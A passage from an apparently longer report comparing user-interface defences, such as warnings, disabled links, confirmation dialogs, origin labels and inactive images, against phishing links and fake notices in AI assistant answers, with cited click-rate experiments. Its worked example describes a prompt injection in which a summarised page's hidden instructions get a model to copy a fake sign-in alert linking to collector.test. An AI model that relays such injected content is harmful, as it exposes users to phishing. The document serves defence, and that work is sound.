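### A delay, or a link that works only inside the warning

Keeping a link from opening for a few seconds helps only if the user can see the address while waiting. TORPEDO uses a three-second delay. Mossano and colleagues found that people recognised more phishing addresses when their attention stayed on the address for four to five seconds, but they call this result preliminary.

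In the *Restricting the Link* experiment, Petelka and colleagues compared a delay with disabling the original link. They gave 1,320 people 15 emails, three with phishing links, and used a milder warning, "This link might be dangerous!" People who saw no warning clicked 87.5% of the phishing links, while those who saw a warning clicked 43.9% on average.

Disabling the original link reduced phishing clicks more than adding a delay did. People clicked 38.5% of phishing links when the original link was disabled and 49.2% when it still worked. They clicked 42.2% with a delay and 50.5% without one. (Each of these averages includes some groups that also had the other feature.) With both features, people clicked 37.5%. Delays of two, three, four and five seconds gave similar results, although a further analysis suggested that five seconds might work slightly better.

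Participants complained more about the delay than about the disabled link. Two also thought the program was using the time to check the link, and that the link was safe once the delay ended. A countdown in a chat app could mislead people in the same way. Disabling the original link looks like the better choice because it had a larger effect and doesn't make people wait. The researchers excluded phones and tablets, but an app could apply the same idea there by making people tap the displayed domain instead of the label.

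### False alarms and warning fatigue

The same researchers also put a false warning on one harmless link. When they disabled the original link, only 32.8% of people clicked through the warning. The groups that received warnings clicked 74% to 81% of similar harmless links without warnings.

People were no more willing to click the harmless link than the phishing links, which suggests that they mostly obeyed the warning and didn't use the address to tell the links apart. The comparison isn't exact, because the harmless link always came after the three phishing links and people became more cautious as they saw more warnings. Still, a false warning on a bank's real login page could turn away many of its customers.

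In both of these experiments, people clicked fewer phishing links as they saw more warnings. Neither showed people clicking frequent warnings away without reading them, which is a common objection to warnings. But participants saw only three or four warnings in a session of about 20 minutes, while someone who uses an assistant at work could see that many every day for years.

False alarms can weaken a warning. In the later experiment, the researchers protected people who clicked a phishing link by sending them to the real company's website, which made the warning look mistaken. Afterwards, 131 participants mentioned trusting the warnings less or clicking through later ones, and more than 50 mentioned past incorrect warnings. An app that warned about every unfamiliar domain would give its users many false alarms, so apps should warn only about links with a specific sign of danger.

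### Confirmation dialogs

A confirmation dialog opens after the user clicks a link, shows the address behind the label and lets the user continue or cancel. OpenAI and Anthropic both use such dialogs for some links. The dialogs work on phones, but the user still has to read the address correctly.

In *URL Inspection Tasks*, 1,573 people in the United States managed an office worker's inbox with 11 genuine emails and three phishing emails. The researchers told them to report anything suspicious, so they may have been more alert than usual. Without help, they visited the phishing site 74.5% of the time. A page that showed the address in large type and asked them to confirm reduced this to 57.2%. The page only slightly reduced visits to genuine links, from 90.6% to 87.9%. People typically spent just three seconds on it.

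The researchers also tested tasks that made people identify the domain before they could continue, by choosing it from a list, highlighting it in the address or typing it. If they got it wrong, a second page showed their answer with the real address and let them choose whether to continue. These tasks reduced phishing visits to 35%.

The more effective tasks made people show where they expected to go, so the program could point out a mismatch. Typing worked especially well against misspelled names such as `googie` for `google`, cutting visits to phishing sites from 79.2% to 17.1%, because people typed the name they expected. Activity alone doesn't explain the improvement. Another group had to drag the pieces of the address into place, a task that nobody could get wrong, and still visited the phishing site 61% of the time.

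The tasks worked less well against phishing domains that begin with a brand name, such as `example-login.com`. People still visited 43% to 46% of these sites. Someone who thinks the company owns such a domain can complete the task correctly and still go to the phishing site.

The tasks also slow people down. Highlighting usually took six or seven seconds and typing took ten. On genuine links, people highlighted the wrong part 29.5% of the time, often by selecting the full address instead of the domain. Visits to genuine links fell to 82.1%, though the drop wasn't statistically significant. The researchers recommend using the tasks only occasionally, as websites do with CAPTCHAs (puzzles that check whether a visitor is human). A chat app could use them only for links to login pages, payment pages and downloads.

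People may turn off a dialog that appears for every link. Proton Mail shows one by default whenever someone clicks a link, but its "Don't ask again" button turns it off for all future links. The email program Thunderbird shows its dialog only for certain warning signs, such as a label that names a different site from the one the link opens. People have less reason to turn off a dialog they seldom see, but comparing the label with the destination misses most disguises.

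### Marking text from outside

An origin label would show which part of an answer came from an outside source. In his interview with TechNadu, Andi Ahmeti of Permiso argued that the app should keep track of untrusted content until it is displayed on the screen. A label such as "From budget.example" beside a link or notice would counter the impression that the assistant's company wrote it. The label could even expose a fake warning that contains only a phone number, which none of the link designs can do.

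A label on text from outside pages wouldn't show whether the source is honest. The app also has to match the text with the page, which is harder when the model has paraphrased it. If the app labels most outside text but misses a paraphrased warning, the missing label could make that warning seem more official.

Labelling individual links, images and copied passages as coming from the page would be more practical than putting one label on the whole answer. Nearly all of a summary comes from the page, so a single label would be accurate but wouldn't separate an attacker's notice from the rest. Matching links against the sources to label them could also reveal an address that appears in no source, which the model may have invented.

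A label that looks like a citation could backfire. Ding and colleagues found that people trusted answers with citations more, even when the citations were random, so a small grey "Source: budget.example" might make a fake notice more convincing. "Copied from budget.example" makes it clearer that the app has only identified where the text came from. Even a well-worded label is passive, though, and the early browser experiment suggests that many people would overlook it.

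### Leaving links and images inactive

An app can also show links from a summarised page as plain text, and images as empty boxes with a "Load image" button. Ahmeti proposed that apps shouldn't fetch images from outside content automatically. This would stop an image from leaking data as soon as the answer appears, and keep a QR code or a picture of a "Sign in" button off the screen until the user loads it.

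The closest experimental evidence on inactive links comes from disabling the original link in the two email experiments. Those links also had warnings, so the results don't show how well disabling links works by itself. Disabling links also doesn't stop determined users. In the 2019 experiment, four participants told Petelka and colleagues that they had opened a suspicious link in a separate window or browser. A fake notice also stays on screen when its link is disabled, and users can still call a phone number in it.

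Deactivating links makes answers less useful, since people often want to open the pages behind them. Microsoft stopped removing such links from Copilot Chat once it could check them when users clicked. A compromise would be to deactivate links only in summaries of pages and emails, where people mainly want the content, and leave them active when someone asks for a website. That would prevent a fake alert in a summary from including a working link, but it would not stop the assistant from linking to a phishing page it found when the user asked where to log in.

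### A separate place for real account notices

A company could show genuine account notices only outside the conversation, in a fixed area the model can't write to, such as the account menu, and tell users that answers never contain them. Any account warning inside an answer would then be false. Unlike an origin label, this rule would also cover paraphrased text.

The design takes up little screen space, but the company would have to keep all real security notices out of the conversation. If it sometimes put one there, users would learn to expect them. Users would also have to remember this rule when a convincing alert appears. The app could add a standard reminder below any answer that seems to discuss the user's account, although the reminder would also appear below some harmless answers.

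An attacker could still try to make part of an answer look like the reserved area. Veit and colleagues include a similar trick in their email catalogue, a fake password prompt that appears to come from the email program. Markdown gives an attacker fewer ways to do this than HTML does, but a picture of an account menu might be enough if the app loads external images.

### One fake alert in three designs

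Suppose again that a user asks a model to summarize a budget.example page about a budgeting tool. The page contains hidden instructions and a ready-made account warning, and the model copies the warning into its answer.

**Ordinary display.**

> The page describes a budgeting tool and compares its two price plans.
>
> **Account:** We noticed a sign-in from a new device. <u>Review it</u>

The screen doesn't show who wrote the warning or where the link goes. On a computer, the user could hover over the link to see that it leads to collector.test, but would need a reason to check.

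**Domain beside the label.**

> The page describes a budgeting tool and compares its two price plans.
>
> **Account:** We noticed a sign-in from a new device. <u>Review it</u> [collector.test]

The user can now see that the link doesn't go to the assistant's website. But the warning still looks like it came from the company, and a user might assume that the company handles logins on another domain. An attacker could encourage that assumption by registering a name like `assistant-login.test`.

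**Outside material marked and switched off.**

> The page describes a budgeting tool and compares its two price plans.
>
> *Copied from budget.example:*
> "Account: We noticed a sign-in from a new device. Review it"
> *Link to collector.test is off.*

Here the user can learn that the warning came from the budgeting page, which has no access to information about sign-ins to the assistant. The link also goes to a site that belongs to neither the budgeting page's owner nor the assistant's. If the model had paraphrased the warning, the app might recognise only the link, and the user would have to infer the rest from it.

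The third display is better against only some attacks. If the user asked for Example Bank's login page and the assistant chose a phishing site from its search results, "Copied from collector.test" would add little to the domain itself. Showing the domain beside the label would be enough for a customer who knows the bank's address. An app that disabled the phishing link would also have to disable the correct one.

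### The designs compared

Numbers in brackets refer to the ten misleading links. The percentages for the full address and the registrable domain are the shares of phishing addresses people detected. For the other tested designs, they are the shares of phishing links people clicked or visited. Percentages from different experiments aren't comparable.

| Design | False or missing label (1–3, 10) | Disguised address (4–7) | Forwarding address (8, 9) | Fake notice | Evidence |
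|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Full address | Shows the destination | Leaves it to the reader | Shows only the first site | No effect | **Tested** in tooltips: 71% of phishing addresses detected |
| Registrable domain | Shows the destination | Removes 4–6, and 7 if encoded | Shows only the first site, unless the app follows the link | No effect | **Tested** in tooltips: 76% detected, not significantly better |
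| Warning beside the link | If the app suspects the link | If the app suspects the link | If the app suspects the link | No effect on the text | **Tested:** 77% without, 30–34% with |
| Warning with the original link disabled | If the app suspects the link | If the app suspects the link | If the app suspects the link | No effect on the text | **Tested:** 77% without, 9–16% with |
| Delay added to a warning | Gives time to read the address | Gives time to read the address | Little effect | No effect on the text | **Tested:** 50.5% without, 42.2% with |
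| Confirmation dialog | Shows the destination | Leaves it to the reader | Shows only the first site | No effect on the text | **Tested:** 74.5% without, 57.2% with |
| Task to identify the domain | Makes the user check | Makes the user check | Checks only the first site | No effect on the text | **Tested:** 74.5% without, 35% with |
| Origin label | Shows who supplied the link | Shows who supplied the link | Shows who supplied the link | Shows the source, if the app can trace it | **Proposed** |
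| Inactive links and images | Prevents a direct click | Prevents a direct click | Prevents a direct click | Leaves the text | **Proposed** |
| Separate area for account notices | No effect | No effect | No effect | Exposes it to users who know the rule | **Proposed** |
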